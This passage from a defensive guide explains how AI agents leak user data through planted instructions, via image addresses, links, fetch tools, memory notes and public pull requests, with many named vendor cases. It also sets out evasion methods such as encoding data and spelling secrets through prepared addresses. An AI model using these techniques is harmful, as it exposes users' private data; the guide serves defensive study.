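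According to Checkmarx, Gemini doesn't display images from outside addresses, but it keeps links unless Google already knows they are malicious. An attacker can avoid this filter by registering a new domain. Checkmarx reported this on 5 October 2025, and Google closed the report four days later as infeasible to fix. Google has a point, because an assistant without links is much less useful, but a user who sees only the words "click here" can't tell that the address behind them contains a password.

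Clients can reduce that risk without removing links. They can show the user the full address before opening it. They can also stop the model from writing addresses at all by having it cite sources by number, with the program inserting the stored address for each one. The model then can't write a secret into the address, although its choice of source could still reveal a little.

Microsoft also declined to fix the Copilot Chat leak that Checkmarx demonstrated. On 4 November 2025 it replied that the attack needed several non-default actions from the user, did not reproduce reliably and came with warnings. Microsoft also assumes that developers review and trust the code they choose to run. A developer who often opens other people's projects should not rely on that assumption.

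### Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy works in the browser, so it doesn't matter how the model wrote the image. The web server sends the rule along with the page. For the router firm's console it could be:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://images.example.com
```

The browser then loads images only from the console's own site and from images.example.com. The `default-src` part applies to resources without a rule of their own, such as fonts, videos and embedded pages. If an answer contains an image from anywhere else, the browser blocks it before sending a request. If a permitted server redirects the browser to another one, the browser checks the new address too. The policy also blocks legitimate images from unlisted sites, and someone has to maintain the list.

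The rule applies only to the page it was sent with, so it has no effect when the same text appears in Slack, Outlook or a developer's log viewer. An image rule also doesn't stop the user from clicking a link. An entry in the rule can name a host and a path, but it can't restrict the query string. If the model can choose the query string, safety depends on what the permitted hosts do with it.

Microsoft's image policy for Copilot had 29 entries when Aim Labs attacked it. One was `*.sharepoint.com`, which covers the SharePoint site of every Microsoft customer, including any attacker who opens an account. The researchers found a SharePoint address that would fetch any address on request, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a similar address in Teams that needed no invitation. The browser requested the "image" from Teams, as the policy permitted,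 and the Teams server passed the data to the attacker.

A policy can also become unsafe without anyone changing it. Agentforce, Salesforce's product for building agents, reads sales enquiries that strangers submit through a web form. In the ForcedLeak attack of September 2025, researchers at the security company Noma planted instructions in an enquiry. When an employee asked the agent about it, the answer included an image whose URL contained sales leads' email addresses. Salesforce's policy restricted where images could load from, but it still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. Willison recounts that the researchers registered the domain and read the data in their own server log.

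Salesforce fixed this by taking back control of the domain and enforcing a list of permitted addresses for its agents' output, according to The Hacker News (2025). A firm with a similar policy needs a named person to check that every listed domain is still in use and still belongs to the right owner, which is much easier with a shorter list.

### Domain allow-lists

Salesforce's new list, Trusted URLs, is used on the server to check the addresses in an agent's output before it reaches a client. The check can therefore stop links as well as images, and it protects clients that have no policy. Its weakness, which Microsoft's filter shared, is that it must find every address in the text. It makes sense to use the browser's rule as well, since that rule still applies when the server's check misses an address in an unusual notation.

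According to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, enforcement starts on 8 September 2025, and administrators must list every outside domain their agents need or risk disruption. An administrator in a hurry will be tempted to permit whole services. The example entry in Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* is docs.google.com. The entry makes sense because the instructions are for customers who connect Google Drive, but anyone can receive data through that host.

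PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack on the email app Superhuman, which had permitted images from docs.google.com. That host also serves Google Forms, and a form can accept an answer written into a web address, so that requesting the address submits the form. The user asked for a summary of recent mail, which included an unopened email with planted text. The assistant's reply contained an image whose address pointed to the attacker's form, with the contents of other emails written in as an answer. The browser requested the image, which submitted the form even though no picture came back.

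This attacker has no web server or request log and sees only the answers to a form. Even so, PromptArmor extracted the full text of several sensitive emails in a single reply and, in another test, parts of more than 40 emails. Superhuman received the report on Friday 5 December 2025, disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and deployed a first patch on Tuesday. It deployed the last patches on 11 January 2026, after PromptArmor had reported further problems.

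The Google Forms route later turned up in OpenAI's Codex, which by then could also triage a user's email. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* dates the report to 21 April 2026, more than three months after the Superhuman case became public. OpenAI has fixed the problem. Vendors evidently don't always recheck their own lists of permitted image sources when another vendor's list fails, so customers should ask whether docs.google.com is permitted.

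A reputable owner is therefore a poor reason to permit a host. It is more useful to ask what a stranger could do there:

- Can anyone open an account and see files, form answers or visitor statistics?
- Does any address on the host store the text it receives?
- Does any address on the host fetch or redirect to another address?
- If the entry has a wildcard, are the answers the same for every subdomain?

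These questions are hard to answer for a big service with thousands of addresses, and the service can add a new feature at any time. The router firm doesn't need to answer them for such a service, because its staff only need pictures of routers. It can keep those on a small site of its own that serves fixed files, has no outside accounts and fetches nothing.

### Image proxies

An image proxy is a server that fetches images on the user's behalf. The client rewrites each image address so that the browser requests the image from the proxy, which requests it from the original server. Email services use proxies to stop senders from learning a reader's network address, and the proxies work well for that purpose.

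Image proxies don't stop a leak if the model writes the image's address. The proxy has to pass the path and query string to the original server to fetch the image, and the secret goes with them. In EchoLeak, the Teams address acted as such a proxy. This made matters worse, because the browser's policy would have blocked a direct request to the attacker's server but allowed one to Teams. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* similarly warns that servers that deliver images for an app can defeat the policy that allows them if they redirect to outside addresses.

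A proxy protects data only if it refuses addresses that the model made up. For example, the vendor's software can sign the address of each image in a document when the document arrives, before the model has read anything. The proxy then fetches only signed addresses, and the model can't forge a signature. Alternatively, the software can save a copy of each image on arrival and serve only the copies, so displaying an answer causes no outside requests.

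Signing does not prevent every leak. An attacker who gets many addresses signed in advance can have the model spell out a secret by choosing among them, which is how the CamoLeak attack worked against GitHub's proxy. Saved copies avoid this as long as outsiders can't see how often users load them, but they take up storage, and a saved copy of a live chart will show old figures. Any proxy that fetches outside addresses must also refuse addresses on the vendor's internal network, or an attacker could use it to reach private servers.

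### Checking before anything appears

Even a sound filter can't prevent a leak if it runs after the client has displayed the text. Most chat clients stream answers, showing the text piece by piece as the model produces it. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search that succeeded because Copilot displayed the text before cleaning it.

The victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft site, and Copilot treated the search query in the link as instructions. It searched the victim's mailbox and began writing an answer that contained an HTML image. Microsoft wrapped the answer in a code block so that the browser would show the HTML as text, but only after the answer was complete. By then the browser had already rendered the image element and requested the image.

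Microsoft's image policy should have stopped a request to the attacker's server, but it allowed requests to Bing, which has a feature that searches for pictures similar to one at a given address. The image element pointed to that feature, so Bing fetched an address on the attacker's server that had an email's subject line in its path. In Varonis' example, the subject line contained a login code. `*.bing.com` was already on the policy that Ravia published in 2025, so anyone checking that list for hosts that fetch other addresses could have found the problem a year earlier.

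Microsoft has patched SearchLeak. The Next Web reports that Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026 and rated it critical. Varonis advises sanitising at the moment of display. The better way for a client to do this is to treat all incoming text as plain text and create an image or link only once its full address has arrived and passed the check. Users notice almost no delay, whereas holding back the whole answer until the check is complete leaves them with an empty screen.

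Asking the user for approval can also come too late. Notion, an app for shared documents, asked users whether they trusted an outside site before its AI added an image from it. But Notion AI had already saved the edit and the browser had requested the image, so the data leaked whatever the user answered. PromptArmor used this to steal the text of a hiring tracker, including salary expectations, with instructions hidden in a CV. A closed report is weak evidence that a product is safe. HackerOne, which screens reports for Notion, had closed the report of this flaw as not applicable, much as Bugcrowd did with the OpenAI report, but Notion put a fix into production on 7 January 2026, the day PromptArmor published.

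AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) covers the latest flaws, found by the same research group that found EchoLeak. Each attack began with an email that the target didn't have to open, and one of them again sent the data out in an image address. Microsoft fixed the three flaws on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November 2026. Fadilpašić (2026), in *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot*, calls ReLeak a campaign to steal data, but the researchers know of no real attacks. Even so, this is the third time in about 18 months that Microsoft has had to stop Copilot from leaking data through images. Customers can't inspect the fixes, but they can test what their own clients load.

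### Checklist

1. List every program that displays the agent's text. Include chat apps, notification emails, log viewers, developer previews and any tool to which staff export conversations.
2. Put hand-written test text into each program, using addresses on a server you control. Try an ordinary image, a reference-style image, an HTML image, a bare link and, if the program draws diagrams, a diagram with a picture. Give each one a different path so that the log shows which of them loaded.
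3. Check the log again a day later, since a notification email or a colleague's review may load the text long after the first display. Record whose network address made each request.
4. Repeat the test with text that arrives slowly, as it does when a model streams it. No request should reach your server at any point, including before the text is complete.
5. If the program asks for approval before adding an image or saving an edit, leave the question unanswered and look at the log.
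6. Turn off link previews for the agent's messages. If the app has no such setting, remove links from the messages or replace them with the name of the site.
7. Block remote images by default. If users need pictures, serve them from a site that holds only fixed files and has no outside accounts.
8. Make the sanitiser check the elements that the client's own parser produces, and have it drop whatever it doesn't recognise.
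9. Read the Content Security Policy that the browser actually receives, on every page that displays agent text. Configuration files don't always match it.
10. For each permitted host, write down who owns it, when the domain registration expires, and whether a stranger could use it to store or forward data. Remove the host if nobody can answer.
11. Show users the full address of a link before it opens.
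12. Find out whether any image proxy accepts addresses that the model has written. If it does, treat it as an open route to the outside.
13. Run the tests again after each update to a client, and before the agent's text goes to a new one.

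## Limiting the addresses an agent may fetch

The image and link leaks described so far depend on a browser or chat app that displays the agent's text. A fetch tool makes its request earlier, while the agent is still working. The model writes an address as a tool argument, the tool requests it, and the server's owner reads the path and query string in the log. The router firm's agent could leak the courier code this way even if the firm ran it without a console. *The Read-Only Lie*, a 2026 post on a personal blog, points out that limiting the tool to reading pages doesn't prevent the leak, because the request for a page carries the data.

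### Requests from the vendor's servers

Deep Research is a mode of ChatGPT that spends up to half an hour reading sources and then writes a report. Users can connect it to Gmail. *ShadowLeak* (2025), by the security company Radware, describes how the company's researchers used one email to steal data through Deep Research. The email contained hidden instructions to find an employee's name and home address in the mailbox and open a URL containing them. When the user asked for research on the day's mail, the agent read the email and opened the URL without displaying anything unusual.

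The first attempts failed because the agent refused a plain instruction and then a disguised one, and it tended to search the web for a suspicious address instead of opening it. The researchers next found out which internal tool opened pages, named it in the email and told the agent to retry after errors. This sometimes worked, but the agent often sent the request without the data. When the email also told the agent to encode the data first, supposedly for security, the attack succeeded in 100% of an unstated number of tests. Radware says this worked because the software making the request received a meaningless string instead of a person's name and address. A filter that searches web addresses for personal details would miss encoded data for the same reason.

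When Dana's browser loaded the attacker's image, the request left her computer, and a proxy on her office network could have logged it. In ShadowLeak, the request went from OpenAI's data centre to the attacker's server. The customer's network carried only an ordinary encrypted session with ChatGPT, so the firm's web gateway, endpoint monitoring and browser policies could not detect the request. Only OpenAI and the attacker could have logged it.

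Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it by early August and marked it as resolved on 3 September. According to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*, Radware saw no real attacks, but this is weak reassurance because the attack leaves no trace outside OpenAI. Customers of any hosted agent should ask whether the vendor logs the full address of every request, including redirects and failures, and lets customers export the log.

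Radware, which sells protection for agents, recommends stripping hidden text from emails and monitoring whether the agent's actions still match the user's goal. Both measures require software to judge the purpose of a text or an agent's actions. A rule limiting which addresses an agent may fetch is easier to verify because a program can check each address without understanding the conversation.

Some products have no such rule. Rovo is an agent that works across Atlassian's products, including Jira for tickets and Confluence for documents. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* (2026) shows it opening an address the model had just composed from private tickets and documents. The attack worked even when an administrator had turned off web search for the whole organisation, because that setting did not remove the tool for opening search results. PromptArmor reported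 this on 23 May and published more than two months later, when Rovo was still vulnerable. An administrator can test the setting by turning web search off, asking the agent to open an address on a server the firm controls, and checking that server's log.

### Listed domains

The simplest rule is a list of permitted domains. It works like this:

1. The model asks for an address.
2. The program takes the host from the address and looks for it on the list.
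3. If the host is there, the program requests the page. Otherwise it returns an error to the model without contacting anyone, which includes looking up the server's name.
4. If the server answers with a redirect, the program goes back to step 2 with the new address.

Developers often forget step 4, because common programming libraries follow redirects automatically. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives redirects as one reason lists of trusted sites are not enough. Many reputable sites have an address that forwards visitors to any destination named in the query string. The model can write a destination that contains the secret, and a check of only the first host will approve the request. A firewall that checks every outgoing connection would block the forwarded request, since it is a new connection to an unlisted host. The firewall would not help if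 the listed site fetched the second address itself, as Bing and Teams did in the attacks on Copilot.

OpenAI's other objection is that people visit far more sites than anyone can list. A strict list produces constant warnings, and users learn to click through them. This is a serious problem for a general assistant but a much smaller one for an agent that reads router manuals.

A list can also fail without any redirect. The browser tool in Antigravity, Google's code editor built around AI agents, came with a default list of permitted sites. One was webhook.site, a testing service for developers where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, which Willison (2025) discussed on 25 November, describes an attack that began when a user gave the agent an integration guide found online. The guide contained instructions in one-point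 type to collect passwords and code from the project and open a webhook.site address with that data in it. The attacker could then read the user's cloud credentials in the site's log.

An agent can bypass an address rule built into one tool if it also has a terminal that can make requests. One editor's protection for a password file failed in the same way. Its file-reading tool refused to open the file, but the model then printed it with a terminal command. Anthropic wrote in a May 2026 engineering post that more capable models are better at getting around restrictions that nobody thought to write down.

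PromptArmor did not report the flaw to Google privately, because Google already warned new users about data theft. PromptArmor also found three other leaks in Antigravity that didn't need the browser tool. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) described another, in which instructions in a web page's title led the agent to read secrets through the terminal and put them in an image that the editor's chat displayed. Removing webhook.site from the list would not stop that attack.

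Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, shows how much can go through a single permitted host. It runs commands in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that can reach only a short list of domains. Anthropic's own API, the interface through which programs use Claude, was on that list. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* appeared in January 2026, two days after the product's release. In its demonstration:

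1. The user connected a folder of property documents and uploaded a skill file they had found online, which contained hidden instructions.
2. The instructions gave the agent an access key belonging to the attacker's Anthropic account.
3. The agent uploaded the largest file it could find to Anthropic's file storage, using that key.
4. The file appeared in the attacker's account, where the attacker could ask Claude questions about it.

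The agent did all this without asking for approval. The attacker received a whole loan document, including parts of social security numbers, which is far more than the few hundred characters a web address would have held. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model, but PromptArmor also got Claude Opus 4.5 to leak customer records the same way. Rehberger had already reported the flaw in Claude's chat product in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*. According to PromptArmor, Anthropic acknowledged that report but did not fix the problem before releasing Cowork.

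InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) explains that Anthropic has since put a proxy in front of its API that accepts only the virtual machine's own session token, so a request with anyone else's key fails. The article concludes more generally that allowing a domain allows every function behind it. A firm that has to allow a cloud service should therefore also restrict which account the agent can use there. This requires a proxy that decrypts the request, or one that adds the right key itself so that the agent never handles any key. A firewall that only forwards the connection isn't enough, because encryption hides the key and the path from it.

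### Addresses the model did not write

A domain list cannot stop the model from writing a secret into an address on a permitted site. A provenance rule targets this leak by letting the fetch tool request only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. The program records each of these addresses and where it came from. If the model follows planted text and adds Dana's order number to an address, the new address isn't in the record, so the tool won't fetch it, however persuasive the planted text was.

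Anthropic's web fetch tool has such a rule. According to the original documentation, which Willison quotes, the tool could fetch addresses that appeared in the user's messages, in the results of the developer's own tools, or in the results of earlier searches and fetches. On first reading, Willison had hoped that the tool would accept only addresses from the user. The longer list worried him, with good reason, because an attacker can put any address on a web page that the agent fetches.

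Ayush Paul showed what this allowed in a post called *The Memory Heist*, published on 9 July 2026. Willison (2026) explains the method in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*. Paul built a website for an imaginary coffee shop, with instructions that AI assistants had to identify their user by browsing an alphabetical directory before they could read the site. The first page linked to one page per letter, each of those linked to pages for the next letter, and so on. If the user's name were Dana, Claude would follow the links for D, DA, DAN and DANA in turn.

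Claude copied every address it requested, character for character, from the previous page. The server generated the pages on demand, and each address included the letters chosen so far, so the last request alone gave Paul the full word. He obtained the user's name, home city and employer, which Claude remembered from earlier chats. The site displayed the instructions only to visitors whose browser string identified them as Claude.

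Anthropic closed the gap by no longer letting the tool follow links found in pages it has fetched. It paid Paul no reward because, it said, its own staff had already found the problem. The restriction also blocks harmless links, so an agent that reads a manual's table of contents can't open chapter 3 from there and has to find it through a search or get the address from the user.

Search results remain a permitted source, so an attacker who gets a few dozen of their own pages into the search engine could still have the model choose among them. This is harder than generating links on the spot, because the attacker must prepare the pages in advance and the search must return them during the conversation.

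According to Anthropic, developers who use the tool through its API can exclude chosen sources from the record with the `url_sources` setting, and the tool refuses any address that is longer than 250 characters or seems to contain credentials the user didn't supply. The length limit prevents the theft of whole documents but leaves room for a password. The credential check may miss encoded data, as the filter in ShadowLeak apparently did. Anthropic's documentation, *Web fetch tool*, advises developers who worry about leaks to limit the number of fetches or the permitted domains, or to turn the tool off.

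A provenance rule can still leak data if the program matches addresses loosely and then requests the model's version. If the program ignores capitalisation when it compares the model's address with the record, the model can encode data by capitalising some letters of a permitted address, and the server's log will show which ones. Ignoring a trailing slash or an extra parameter causes a similar leak. The safest method is to use the model's text only to find the matching entry, and then to request the stored copy.

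### How OpenAI came to use a public index

OpenAI adopted its current rule after several earlier ones failed. The first, in December 2023, was a feature called `url_safe`. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web page checked with an OpenAI server whether the image's address was safe. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the feature half-baked and noted that the iPhone app didn't have it yet. He also expected attackers to find ways to hide data in subdomains or file names.

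OpenAI didn't publish how it decided which addresses were safe, so Rehberger worked some of it out by experiment. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* reports that addresses under windows.net passed the check. Microsoft rents out storage under that domain, and customers can read the logs of requests to their own storage. Rehberger opened an account there and had ChatGPT load an image whose address contained the user's recent chat history. He had reported this weakness and several others in October 2024, and some still worked when he wrote the post.

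The check also covered only images. Radware found no comparable limit on the pages Deep Research could open, so the check did not apply to ShadowLeak. After that attack, OpenAI restricted ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as it had received them, even if instructions told it to add something.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* (2026) gets around this much as Paul's coffee shop did six months later. The attacker's email contained a ready-made address for each letter and digit, and the agent opened the matching ones in turn to spell out the data. Because requests can arrive out of order, the researchers prepared separate addresses for each character position. Spelling ten characters this way takes 360 addresses, 36 for each position, which fit easily in an email.

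ZombieAgent also defeated a rule about where addresses came from. ChatGPT would not open an attacker's address stored in its memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. Radware used a shared file to plant a different note, an instruction to reread a certain email whenever the user wrote something. ChatGPT was still permitted to open the addresses in that email, so the theft continued in every new chat. Designers of such a rule have to consider whether planted text can bring an address back through a source that the rule accepts.

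Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to Ars Technica's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* (2026), ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link appears in a well-known public index or the user supplied it directly in the chat.

OpenAI explained the wider rule on 28 January 2026, in the post cited above and in a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that discovers web pages by following links and records their addresses. Before an agent automatically loads a page or an image, the software checks whether that exact address is in the record. The agent can load the address if it is there; otherwise, the software tells the agent to try another site or warns the user before loading it.

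This rule would have stopped ShadowLeak, because no crawler had seen an address ending in that employee's encoded details. It would also have stopped Rehberger's windows.net image, even though the domain is reputable. OpenAI says the rule is meant to prevent quiet leaks through the address itself and does not make a page's content trustworthy.

### Testing the argument for a public index

The case for the rule rests on three premises:

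1. An address in the public index contains no private data about this user.
2. The crawler builds the index independently of users, with no access to their conversations or accounts.
3. An attacker learns little from which public address the agent requests.

If all three hold, the agent can fetch any indexed address without leaking much.

**Public addresses and private data.** OpenAI says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's data, and some public addresses contain secrets. For *The Silent Spill* (2026), Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues collected 6,094,475 addresses from web archives, paste sites and services that scan links for malware. Their software flagged 12,331 as exposing something sensitive, including 26 links for resetting passwords and 83 API keys. The largest group, 5,343, involved login tokens and similar credentials. The researchers checked 30 of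 these by hand and found that 27 were genuine.

The flagged addresses make up 0.2% of the collection, but the researchers searched for domains and keywords they expected to be risky, so this figure doesn't estimate the share in the web as a whole or in OpenAI's index. The way the secrets became public is still relevant to both. Email providers and company security systems automatically send suspicious links to scanning services, and some of those services publish what they receive. So a private link in Dana's mailbox could become public without her doing anything, and a crawler that reads the scanning service's reports could pick it up.

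This weakens the premise only partly, because if Dana's reset link is already in a public index, an attacker doesn't need her agent to steal it. Fetching the link also doesn't send it to anyone except the site that issued it. The agent is more likely to cause harm by using up the link or by confirming something when it opens it, which is a reason to exclude addresses with long random tokens even when they are public.

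**Independence from users.** OpenAI says its crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. Outsiders can't check this, but the design is sensible and a vendor could have an auditor confirm it. This independence would be lost if the company later added addresses that its users' agents had visited, perhaps to keep the index fresh. An address composed to contain a secret would then be permitted once one user had approved it.

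Looking up an address can also leak any secret it contains. A smaller firm without a crawler might send each address to an outside service to ask whether it is known. The service then receives the secret regardless of its answer. If the service publishes the addresses submitted to it, as some scanners do, the check also makes the secret public. The firm therefore has to run the lookup on a local copy of the index or use a provider it trusts to see every address.

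Attackers can get addresses into even a truly independent index, because anyone can publish web pages. Dana's order number has five digits, so an attacker could publish 100,000 addresses, one for each possible number, and wait for the crawler. If it recorded them all, the index would include an address containing her order number, although nobody involved had ever had access to her mail. The attacker would learn the number from which address her agent fetched. A crawler might well ignore 100,000 nearly empty pages, but the attacker could instead publish 50 addresses, one for each possible digit in each position, and have the agent fetch one per position.

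Most of the remaining risk comes from which address the agent fetches. Ramadan and colleagues use a page about cancer support as an example of an address that is sensitive without leaking anything. The page's owner can still tell from the fetch that somebody wanted it, and planted text can assign any meaning to any page. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI's paper acknowledges this problem. An attacker with an ordinary blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for one to stand for each letter and digit, and a choice among 36 addresses carries about five bits of information. With thousands of pages, each could stand for a whole word.

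Rehberger suggests either caching each page for a few minutes, so that a second visit makes no request, or forbidding the agent to open the same address twice in a session. He had not tested whether ChatGPT already did either. Both measures would hinder an attacker who has one page per letter, since spelling "Dana" requires opening the page for A twice. But they would not have stopped ZombieAgent, which used separate addresses for each position, or Paul's directory, where every address was new.

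Limiting the number of requests works against all of these, but the right limit depends on the length of the secret. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) describes an early attack that sent one character per request. At the time, ChatGPT allowed ten addresses per prompt, so the attacker could get ten characters, more than enough for a six-digit reset code.

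If the vendor has kept the crawled pages as well as their addresses, it is better to give the agent the stored copy. The page's owner then receives no request, so they can't learn anything from which page the agent chose. The copy may be out of date, which is fine for a router manual but not for a train timetable.

Redirects are less of a risk here than under a domain list. The index contains whole addresses, including query strings, so the model can't write a secret into the destination. The one exception is when the agent uses a browser in which Dana is logged in. A public address such as "my account" can then redirect to one that contains her user name or a login token, which the site adds after the first address has been checked. The software should therefore look up each new address in the index before following it, and should fetch public pages without the user's cookies.

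### Addresses in the user's message

Both companies' rules make an exception for addresses the user supplies. This is probably unavoidable, since people expect an assistant to open a link they give it. Rehberger believes that an address in a user's message counts as safe for the rest of the ChatGPT session, even if it is not in the index.

People paste text they haven't written and often haven't read. A website like the one in Samoilenko's attack could add 360 addresses to whatever a visitor copies, and all of them would then be in the user's own message. The 2024 study of ChatGPT suggests refusing to open links whenever a prompt contains pasted text. This would be safe, but it would annoy everyone who pastes a link. A narrower rule would accept an address if it is the only one in the message, because an attacker can't leak much with a single address. If the message contains several, the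 agent would check them against the index.

The exception is more dangerous in automated systems, where a "user message" may not come from the user. At the router firm, a program could send the model a customer's ticket as a user message. Every address in the ticket would then count as user-supplied, although a stranger wrote it. The firm should pass tickets to the model as tool results and not add addresses from them to the record of permitted addresses. This won't stop the model from obeying instructions in a ticket, but the fetch tool applies its rule regardless of what the model does.

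### Tools that skip the check

Several of these leaks occurred in products whose makers already had a suitable check but had not applied it everywhere. `url_safe` was missing from ChatGPT's Mac and iPhone apps and from Deep Research's browsing tool. Atlassian's setting covered searching but not fetching. Rehberger warns that OpenAI's new rule could also be applied inconsistently, because some of the company's developers might not know about it.

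The remedy is to enforce the rule at a point that all requests must pass through. If every tool runs inside one virtual machine whose only connection is a proxy, a tool the firm forgot to configure fails to connect, and somebody notices. Separate checks for each tool are riskier because a tool without a check still works, and an attacker may be the first to discover the omission. The firm also has to know which tools run elsewhere. For example, Anthropic's *Web tools* explains that in versions of Claude Desktop that use another company's cloud, fetching follows the customer's list of permitted domains, but the cloud provider runs the searches. A firewall around the desktop app would not affect those searches.

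OpenAI also offers a stricter option called Lockdown Mode. According to Willison (2026), it limits outgoing network requests to prevent the last step of a data theft, and OpenAI is rolling it out to personal as well as business accounts. It suits people who handle sensitive data and can do without some of ChatGPT's web features.

### A rule for the support agent

The router firm's agent fetches pages to read manuals and to see what customers have linked to. It might also look up a parcel on the courier's website, where the page's address includes the parcel number. The table shows how each rule affects these jobs and the main attacks.

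| | Listed domains | Addresses the model did not write | Addresses in a public index |
|---|---|---|---|
| Manual on the maker's website | Works if the site is listed | Works if a search or an employee supplied the address | Works if the crawler has found it |
| Page a customer links to | Usually fails | Works only if addresses in tickets count | Works if the page is public |
| Parcel lookup | Works if the courier is listed | Fails | Fails |
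| Code written into an address on the attacker's site | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked unless the attacker had that exact address indexed |
| Code written into an address on a listed site with public logs | Gets through | Blocked | Blocked unless the attacker had that exact address indexed |
| Code spelled out with prepared addresses on the attacker's site | Blocked | Gets through if they came from an accepted source | Gets through if the attacker's pages are indexed |

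If the firm requires an address to satisfy both a domain list and a provenance rule, an attacker needs a gap in each. If satisfying either rule is enough, an attacker can use whichever is weaker. OpenAI takes the second approach, accepting an address if it is indexed or the user supplied it.

For manuals, the firm doesn't need a general rule at all. It can list the exact addresses of a few hundred pages and have the tool work like this:

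```
fetch(address):
    entry = exact match for address in the list
    if there is no entry, or the job has used up its requests:
        refuse, before looking up the server's name
    request entry.stored_address, without cookies or text from the model
    if the server redirects:
        refuse, unless the new address is also in the list
```

The model can still choose which of the listed pages to fetch, but only the owners of those sites see its choice. If the firm downloads the manuals once a week and serves its own copies, nobody outside the firm sees which pages the model chooses.

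The parcel lookup needs a separate tool that accepts only a parcel number. The tool should build the address itself and check that the number belongs to the current ticket. Otherwise the model could submit the courier code as a parcel number, and the courier's website would receive the code.

Pages that customers link to are the hardest to handle safely, because a stranger chooses both the address and the content. None of the three rules makes it safe for the agent to open them while the courier code is in its context. The firm could have a second agent, without access to the code, read these pages. It could also choose not to open them at all, since a customer who wants to show a fault can attach a photograph to the ticket.

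## Checking text that other people and services can read

Even if the router firm removes its agent's fetch tool and shows all summaries as plain text, the agent still posts bug reports on a public tracker. An attacker who gets the agent to put the courier code in a report can read it there.

Whether such text leaks data depends on who can read it. The table shows what access an attacker needs to read each kind of text.

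| Text | What the attacker needs |
|---|---|
| Tool argument | Control of the tool, or access to a log or screen that shows its arguments |
| Tool result repeated in an answer | To be the person talking to the agent, or to read a place where someone posts the answer |
| Search query | Control of the search service, or access to its logs or statistics |
| Issue, pull request or commit in a public project | A web browser |
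| The same in a private project | An account with access to that project |
| Reply on a support ticket | To have opened the ticket, or to share the customer's account |
| Shared document | An invitation, or the link if anyone with the link can open it |

### Tool arguments

If a tool's provider is honest and keeps its logs private, an outside attacker never sees the arguments an agent sends to the tool. But many agents connect to tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard, and an attacker can publish an MCP server, the program that provides the tools. The model relies on the server's description of each tool to decide what to put in the arguments, so a dishonest provider can request extra information, for instance by adding a "background" field and describing it as required.

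A provider can also change the description after a firm has approved the tool. TechRepublic's *Microsoft Flags MCP Tool Descriptions as Hidden AI Agent Attack Path* covers a July 2026 warning about this. The tool's name and the summary people see can stay the same while the text that guides the model changes, and the agent may still appear to finish its task normally. The article recommends listing approved servers and publishers and turning off settings that allow every server. A firm should also save a copy of each description and have someone review any change before the agent uses it.

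Other people may be able to see the arguments too. daily.dev's *Azure SRE Agent flaw lets outsiders silently eavesdrop on enterprise cloud operations* describes a flaw, CVE-2026-32173, in the live activity stream of Azure SRE Agent, a Microsoft agent that helps run cloud systems. The server checked that a visitor had a valid Microsoft business account but not that the account belonged to the right organisation. Outsiders could therefore read users' prompts, credentials and commands with their full arguments, without leaving a trace on the victim's side. They didn't need prompt injection, because the agent's ordinary activity already contained the secrets.

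### Search queries

A search query is also a tool argument. If the router firm's agent searches for an error message and includes the customer's name and address, the search provider receives them, even if nobody has attacked the agent.

An outside attacker normally can't see what someone types into a general search engine. Some engines show site owners which queries brought up their pages, but Google omits rare queries from these reports, and a query containing one person's order number would be very rare. The risk is greater when the agent uses the search box on a smaller site, because the site's owner can log every query. Inside a company, a search page that lists recent or popular queries can show colleagues information they aren't allowed to see.

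The firm can limit this by replacing free-text search with a tool that accepts only a router model and an error code from fixed lists. The agent then can't search for unusual faults, but it also can't send the provider a customer's address.

### Tool results repeated in an answer

Suppose a customer asks a shop's AI assistant when a parcel will arrive. The assistant looks up the order with a tool that returns the whole record, including an internal note that the shop suspects the customer of fraud. If the assistant repeats the note in its reply, the customer will see it.

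The simplest remedy is a tool that returns only the fields this person may see. The shop's tool could return only the delivery date, so the model would have no private note to repeat. Developers should also check whether the product displays raw tool results, perhaps in a panel added for debugging, since those appear regardless of what the model writes.

### A private repository in a public pull request

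GitHub is a site where developers keep code in projects called repositories. On a public repository, anyone with an account can open an issue, which is a bug report or suggestion, or a pull request, which proposes a change. GitHub's MCP server lets an agent open both through the user's account.

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), published on 26 May, describes an attack on a test account that owned a simple public Pac-Man game and several private repositories:

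1. The attacker opened an issue on the game's repository with instructions for an agent in its text.
2. The owner asked Claude 4 Opus, running in the Claude Desktop app, to look at the open issues.
3. The agent went through the issues, reached the planted one and followed it. It read the private repositories, so their contents joined the context.
4. The agent wrote what it had found into a new pull request on the game's repository.
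5. The repository was public, so the attacker could read the pull request like anyone else.

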